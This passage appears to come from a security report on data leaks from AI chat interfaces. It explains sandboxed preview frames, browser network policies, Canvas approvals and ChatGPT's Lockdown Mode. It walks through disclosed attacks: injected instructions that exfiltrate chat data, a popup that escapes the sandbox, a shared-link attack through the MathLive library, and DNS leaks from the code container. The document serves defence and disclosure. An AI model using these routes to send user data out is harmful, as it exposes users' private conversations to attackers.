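For data split across several requests, Lan and colleagues suggest limiting the number of requests in a session and examining them together. They also propose taint tracking, which they didn't test. The system would mark all text from web pages as untrusted, along with anything the model wrote under its influence. It would then block any web request containing a marked value, or ask the user to approve it. This could catch a four-character fragment that looks harmless, because the check depends on where the text came from. But a model's whole answer depends on its whole context, so once the assistant had read one web page, a cautious version of the rule would mark everything it wrote, and the user would be back to approving every request.

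No display control covers requests from a model's code-execution container, the isolated computer on which it runs programs it has written. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (March 2026) describes a flaw that let ChatGPT's container send out conversation data in the names of servers it looked up. OpenAI had fixed the flaw on 20 February.

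## Previews of HTML and small apps inside a chat

ChatGPT's code container runs a model's programs on OpenAI's servers. Many chat interfaces also run programs in the user's browser. If a customer asks the shopping assistant for a page that tracks three deliveries, the model can write one in HTML, with a script that counts down the days. The interface can then show the working page inside the chat. According to OpenAI's *Working with writing blocks and code blocks in ChatGPT*, ChatGPT can preview HTML pages, SVG images, Mermaid diagrams and components built with React, a library for making interactive pages.

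An image rule can't protect a previewed page, because a script can also contact a server directly, submit a form, load a font or open a window. The script can put an address together from pieces while it runs, so the complete address never appears in the text that a sanitiser inspects. The interface can't remove everything that might send a request, because the user asked for a working program. It has to run the code and limit what the code can reach.

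### The sandboxed frame

Browsers let a page display another page inside a frame. A script in either page can read cookies, stored data and page content only from its own origin, which is the first part of its web address, chiefly the host name. A chat company can therefore isolate previews by serving them from a different host. Goyal (2026) found in *Do the Math* that ChatGPT did this, and that code in a preview could not read the chat page around it.

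ChatGPT didn't always separate files this way. Imperva's *XSS Marks the Spot* describes how ChatGPT displayed an uploaded HTML file under a temporary address that the browser treats as part of the page that created it. Only the browser policy stopped the file's script from running. The policy allowed scripts with the right nonce, a code that a server should change for every request. ChatGPT's nonce never changed, so the researcher copied it into a new file and the script ran.

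The company can also put the frame in a sandbox, which makes the browser withhold most of a page's usual powers. The site then grants back the ones it needs:

```
<iframe sandbox="allow-scripts" src="https://preview.example/"></iframe>
```

| Permission | What the framed page can do with it |
|---|---|
| `allow-scripts` | Run scripts |
| `allow-same-origin` | Keep the origin of its own address, with the cookies and storage that belong to it |
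| `allow-forms` | Submit forms |
| `allow-top-navigation` | Replace the whole chat page with another page |
| `allow-popups` | Open new windows |
| `allow-popups-to-escape-sandbox` | Open new windows that have none of the sandbox's restrictions |

Without `allow-same-origin`, the browser gives a sandboxed preview an origin that matches no other, so the preview can't read any site's cookies. Granting both `allow-same-origin` and `allow-scripts` is dangerous if the preview comes from the chat's own host, because the preview's script can then access the chat page and remove its own sandbox.

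A frame inside a sandboxed frame has at least the same restrictions as the outer one. A window opened from a sandboxed frame normally inherits its restrictions too. This can break ordinary links, since a shop's website may not work in a window that can't use cookies. Developers therefore have a reason to grant the last permission in the table.

The sandbox protects the user's login and other conversations, but it doesn't stop outgoing requests. Even a frame with no permissions can load an image from any server. The preview can also leak information from the chat without reading the chat, because the model may already have written the order number into the preview's code.

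### A network policy for the frame

The chat page's own list of image sources doesn't cover requests from a preview on another host. The preview needs its own browser policy, which can be much stricter than the one for the chat:

```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'none';
  script-src 'unsafe-inline'; style-src 'unsafe-inline';
  img-src data:; form-action 'none'; base-uri 'none'
```

`'unsafe-inline'` allows scripts written directly into the page. Websites usually avoid it because it would also let an attacker's injected script run. Here the whole page is already untrusted, and the sandbox prevents it from accessing the account. The `data:` entry allows images embedded in the page. The delivery tracker would work under this policy, but it couldn't load a photo from a server or fetch the parcel's current position.

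This policy still lets a script navigate its own frame to a new address, such as one on images.example that contains the order number. The chat page can prevent that with `frame-src`, which lists the addresses its frames may load. WebRTC connections also need to be blocked separately. Chrome's Connection Allowlists cover both frame navigation and WebRTC.

### Who decides which servers an app may contact

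Many useful apps need the network, for example to load a drawing library for a chart or fetch a weather forecast. Chat companies handle this need in different ways.

OpenAI's Canvas feature, a workspace beside the ChatGPT conversation for editing text and code, can run HTML and React code in a sandbox. In *What is the canvas feature in ChatGPT*, OpenAI warns that a web preview could send a third party information that the user has shared with ChatGPT. ChatGPT therefore asks the user before a preview contacts a third party that OpenAI doesn't know about. OpenAI describes the same approach for ChatGPT Apps, which other companies build, and says the sandbox can detect unexpected communications.

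A company could build such a prompt from the browser's own tools:

1. The preview's policy blocks every outside server.
2. The app tries to contact one, and the browser refuses and reports the attempt to the preview page.
3. The preview page passes the report to the chat, which asks the user about that server.
4. If the user agrees, the chat reloads the preview with that server added to the policy.

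The prompt has the same weaknesses as a "load this image?" button, and it is harder to ignore because an app may not work until the user agrees. Approval in Canvas is also broader, since it covers communication with the third party rather than a single request. A script could therefore make a harmless first request and put the order number in the second. OpenAI's help page doesn't list the third parties that OpenAI already knows, and those need the same scrutiny as the hosts in a browser policy.

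For Enterprise customers, OpenAI leaves Canvas's code execution on and its network access off unless an administrator changes the settings. With network access off, some previews never finish loading because they need a library from another server. A company could avoid many of these failures by keeping copies of common libraries on the preview's host.

In *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts*, Willison (2026) calls these sandboxed apps the artifacts pattern, a name that Anthropic's Claude made familiar. When Anthropic introduced artifacts in 2024, a fixed policy let them load scripts from a public host of common libraries but blocked contact with other outside servers, and the user had nothing to approve. This is safer than asking the user for permission, but the apps can't show live data.

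The Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting AI applications to outside tools, has an extension that lets a tool display its own small app in the chat. The developer lists the domains the app needs, and the chat application uses that list to set a policy for the app's frame. A shop's delivery app might list only the shop's server. If an injected instruction then inserted an image address on images.example into the app, the browser would refuse to load the image.

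The chat company can review the declaration before the app runs, and a recipe app that declares an advertising network would stand out. But the declaration itself doesn't protect users against the developer, who can list any server.

### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI's strictest protection against leaks is Lockdown Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting that turns off the features that could cause them. OpenAI announced it on 13 February 2026 for the Enterprise, Edu, Healthcare and Teachers plans. On 4 June it began offering the setting to personal accounts, including free ones, and to small businesses that manage their own subscriptions.

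| Feature | With Lockdown Mode on |
|---|---|
| Web browsing | Cached pages only |
| Images | ChatGPT may not show them in ordinary answers or fetch them from the web; uploading and generating images still work |
| Deep Research and Agent Mode, in which ChatGPT carries out tasks on websites | Off |
| Canvas | The user can't approve network access |
| Files | ChatGPT can't download them for analysis but can use ones the user uploads |
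| Connected services on personal accounts | No live access and no changes to outside data |

OpenAI describes the mode as deterministic. The software turns these features off regardless of what the model has read or decided, so an attacker can't turn them back on by sending an email that persuades the model. Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, welcomed this because the decision doesn't depend on an AI system that an attacker could also fool. Withholding images from answers, as GitHub did in Copilot Chat, also prevents a slower leak, in which a model spells out a secret by choosing among public image addresses.

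The mode limits or disables several ChatGPT features. Somebody comparing shoes may get no pictures and out-of-date search results, and ChatGPT's shopping agents and personal finance feature don't work at all. Users also can't combine the mode with Developer Mode, according to Help Net Security's *OpenAI is locking down parts of ChatGPT to reduce data theft risks* (2026). Connectors on personal accounts can still use data that OpenAI has already copied from a service, because searching the copy sends no request to the service.

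In workplaces with managed accounts, administrators choose which apps remain available. OpenAI advises them against allowing apps they don't trust or any action that writes something where outsiders might see it. A comment on a public project page could leak an order number, just as an image address could. Reading from a trusted app is less risky, but it still brings private data into the model's context.

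Lockdown Mode doesn't change ChatGPT's memory, and users can turn the mode off for a single chat. An instruction that an attacker planted in memory, as in Radware's ZombieAgent attack, could therefore take effect in a chat where the mode is off. The mode also doesn't affect network access in Codex, from which PromptArmor extracted emails in April.

In its February announcement, OpenAI wrote that the mode is "not necessary for most users" and listed executives and security teams at prominent organisations as examples of people who might want it. In a post that Willison quotes, Dane Stuckey, the company's head of information security, similarly wrote that the mode was worth the lost features for people at higher risk because of who they are, what they work on or the data they handle.

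Willison concluded that if ChatGPT needs a special mode to cut off these leaks, its default settings must not offer robust protection against a determined attacker. OpenAI's announcement supports this inference. The company wrote that some network features carry risks that the industry's protections don't yet fully address, and it now labels such features "Elevated Risk".

OpenAI's advice is reasonable for people who haven't connected ChatGPT to anything private, but harder to accept for people who have connected a mailbox. An attacker can send the same email to thousands of ordinary addresses, and a bank login code is worth stealing even from someone who isn't an executive.

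### The popup that escaped Lockdown Mode

In Lockdown Mode, users could no longer approve network access for Canvas code, but ChatGPT still ran HTML previews. Check Point Research, which had found the hidden route out of ChatGPT's code container, found another through these previews.

ChatGPT displayed previews in nested sandboxed frames. OpenAI had tried to keep previews from opening windows by intercepting the function that scripts use for this, but the sandbox still granted both popup permissions, including the one that lets new windows escape the sandbox. In The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026), Check Point's head of research, Eli Smadja, explains how the researchers bypassed the interception. Their page created another frame inside itself, and that frame had its own unmodified copy of the function. The window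 opened with that copy was outside the sandbox and Lockdown Mode's limits, so its code could send data to the researchers.

OpenAI had changed one copy of a function on a page where the attacker could make more copies. If the sandbox had withheld the popup permissions, the browser would have blocked popups from every copy.

Browsers usually block popups unless the user has just clicked something, so this leak would normally have needed one click. The exception was ChatGPT Classic, OpenAI's older desktop app for Windows and macOS. Clubic's *Même avec son mode de verrouillage activé, ChatGPT laissait fuiter des conversations* explains that OpenAI built the app with Electron, a tool for turning a website into a desktop program, and that the app's built-in browser opened windows without requiring a click. The victim only had to chat with a GPT (a customised version of ChatGPT that anyone can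 make and share) that the attacker had prepared. The victim's messages then went to the attacker's server with no sign on the screen.

The researchers could also use the window to show a fake update that offered malware, because it had ChatGPT's icon and they controlled its content. The victim still had to click the download link. If the victim was logged out, the researchers could redirect the main window to a fake login page.

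OpenAI removed both popup permissions on 18 September 2026, and the researchers confirmed that their method no longer worked. TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* reports that OpenAI fixed the problem on its servers, so desktop app users didn't have to install an update. Check Point's findings became public in early November. OpenAI will close ChatGPT Classic on 30 January 2027.

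### The shared link that reached the account

Check Point's window bypassed the network limits. In October, Goyal and colleagues at Parameter found another flaw in HTML previews that broke the separation between a preview and the user's account. An attacker could publish a ChatGPT conversation through the normal sharing feature and send someone the link. When a logged-in user opened it, the attacker's code could read that user's private conversations, send them to an outside server and act in ChatGPT as that user.

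The conversation contained an HTML preview and an interactive graph. To draw the graph, ChatGPT loaded MathLive, a library for mathematical formulas that includes an on-screen keyboard. MathLive set up a receiver in the chat page for messages about the keyboard. Browsers let frames from different origins send each other messages, so the preview could send one to the chat page even though it couldn't access the page directly. The receiver has to check who sent each message, but MathLive's accepted messages from anyone.

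| Protection in ChatGPT | How the attack got past it |
|---|---|
| The preview ran on a separate host | It sent MathLive a new keyboard layout containing HTML, which MathLive added to the chat page |
| The preview's frame had a sandbox | The added HTML created a new frame, without a sandbox and with the chat page's origin |
| The browser policy blocked scripts written into the page | The policy allowed scripts from YouTube, and one YouTube address returned code that the researchers had put in the request |

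The last step resembles the leaks through Google's and Microsoft's domains, except that the attacker used the trusted host to load code into the chat page rather than to send data out. Willison notes that this code could then send out the stolen text in an image reference.

Goyal's first working version was much less dangerous because the victim had to connect an app that the researchers controlled. The researchers then tried an HTML attachment, but the shared copy of the conversation lost the graph. Without the graph, MathLive didn't load, and nothing received the preview's messages. The attack worked after they put both a graph and a preview into the conversation itself. At first the victim had to press the Preview button once. In a later version, ChatGPT opened the preview automatically, and the attack worked in all three attempts with a separate account.

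The researchers reported the flaw on 18 October and OpenAI fixed it on 26 October, according to Infobae's *Un fallo de ChatGPT permitía acceder a conversaciones privadas* (2026). OpenAI paid them $5,000, which Willison thought a bit low for such a serious flaw. Parameter found no sign that anyone had used it against real users. On 31 October, MathLive's developers released a version that by default accepts messages only from the page's own origin, which also protects other sites that use the library.

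### Features the list leaves out

OpenAI defines Lockdown Mode by the features it turns off. An attacker needs only one route missing from that list, and a product that changes every month keeps adding new routes. In December 2024, Willison noticed that Python code in Canvas could contact any server from the user's browser after a general warning, even though ChatGPT's older Python tool had no network access.

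OpenAI's help page for the mode lists Canvas networking but doesn't mention HTML previews. Willison's impression is that previews are the latest version of Canvas, but users can't tell from the page whether the restriction covers both. OpenAI also warns there that "unforeseen combinations of capabilities" may still leak data. Parameter's attack fits that description, since a reviewer who examined the graph and the preview separately could have passed both.

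Testing every pair of features soon becomes impractical. Twenty features make 190 pairs, and Parameter's attack also relied on an entry in the browser policy. It is more manageable to deny network access by default at a level that every feature has to pass through, and to grant exceptions one feature at a time. A browser policy that starts from `default-src 'none'` does this for one page. For Lockdown Mode, OpenAI could list the features that stay on, so that a new kind of preview would be off until someone had reviewed it.

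A desktop app makes this easier, because the company controls the browser inside it. Electron lets developers refuse new windows and inspect each web request before the app sends it. ChatGPT Classic could have refused every connection to servers outside OpenAI's network while Lockdown Mode was on. Check Point's window would still have opened but couldn't have sent anything. A website can't control the user's browser like this, so in a locked chat on the web, the safest choice is to show the HTML as code without running it.
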